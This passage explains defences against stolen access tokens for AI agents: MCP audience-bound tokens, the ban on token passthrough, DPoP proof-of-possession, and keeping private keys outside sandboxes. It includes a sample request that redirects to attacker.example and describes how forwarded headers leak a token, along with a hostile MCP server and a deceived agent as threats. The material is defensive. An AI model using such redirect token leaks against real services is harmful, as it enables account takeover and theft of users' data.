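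Limiting a token to one recipient is much more useful when that recipient is the dishonest party. If an agent connects to a hostile MCP server with a token that also works for the user's mail service, the server could read the mail. The Model Context Protocol's authorization rules therefore require clients to request a token for a particular server, and servers to reject tokens issued for anyone else. The rules also forbid token passthrough, in which a server forwards the client's token to another service. The server must get a separate token for that service. Vercel applies the same idea to requests that its firewall forwards to an operator's own proxy. Each request carries a token whose audience is the proxy's exact URL, and the proxy should check for an exact match.

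The strongest protection ties the token to a cryptographic key. DPoP, short for Demonstrating Proof of Possession, is an IETF standard from 2023, RFC 9449. The client creates a pair of keys, one private and one public, and the issuer ties the token to the public key. For each request, the client signs a short proof with the private key:

```
GET /go?to=https://attacker.example/a HTTP/1.1
Host: docs.example
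Authorization: DPoP ACCESS-TOKEN
DPoP: SIGNED-PROOF

The proof contains
  method       GET
  URL          https://docs.example/go
  time         10:12:44
  identifier   a value for this proof only
  token hash   a fingerprint of ACCESS-TOKEN
```

The server checks the signature and compares the proof with the request. If a library forwards both headers to `attacker.example`, the attacker gets the token and one proof. That proof is valid only for a short time and only for a GET request to `/go`, the redirect page. The attacker could change the query, which the proof doesn't cover, but couldn't fetch `/private/billing`. If the client signs a new proof for the second hop, that proof names `attacker.example` and is useless at `docs.example`. Servers can also store the identifiers of recent proofs and reject any that are reused.

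DPoP fails if the thief gets the private key as well, so the key shouldn't be in the sandbox. Docker already does something similar for SSH, a protocol for logging in to other machines. Programs in its sandbox can get signatures from the user's computer but can't copy the private key. A deceived agent can still get signatures on requests that harm the user.

A broker that only replaces placeholders can't produce DPoP proofs, because each proof needs a fingerprint of the real token and a fresh signature. The broker would have to hold the private key and sign a proof for each request, which an operator could program in a function like Cloudflare's. The service also has to support DPoP, because one that doesn't may accept a stolen token without any proof. DPoP doesn't protect a fixed key sent in `X-Api-Key`.
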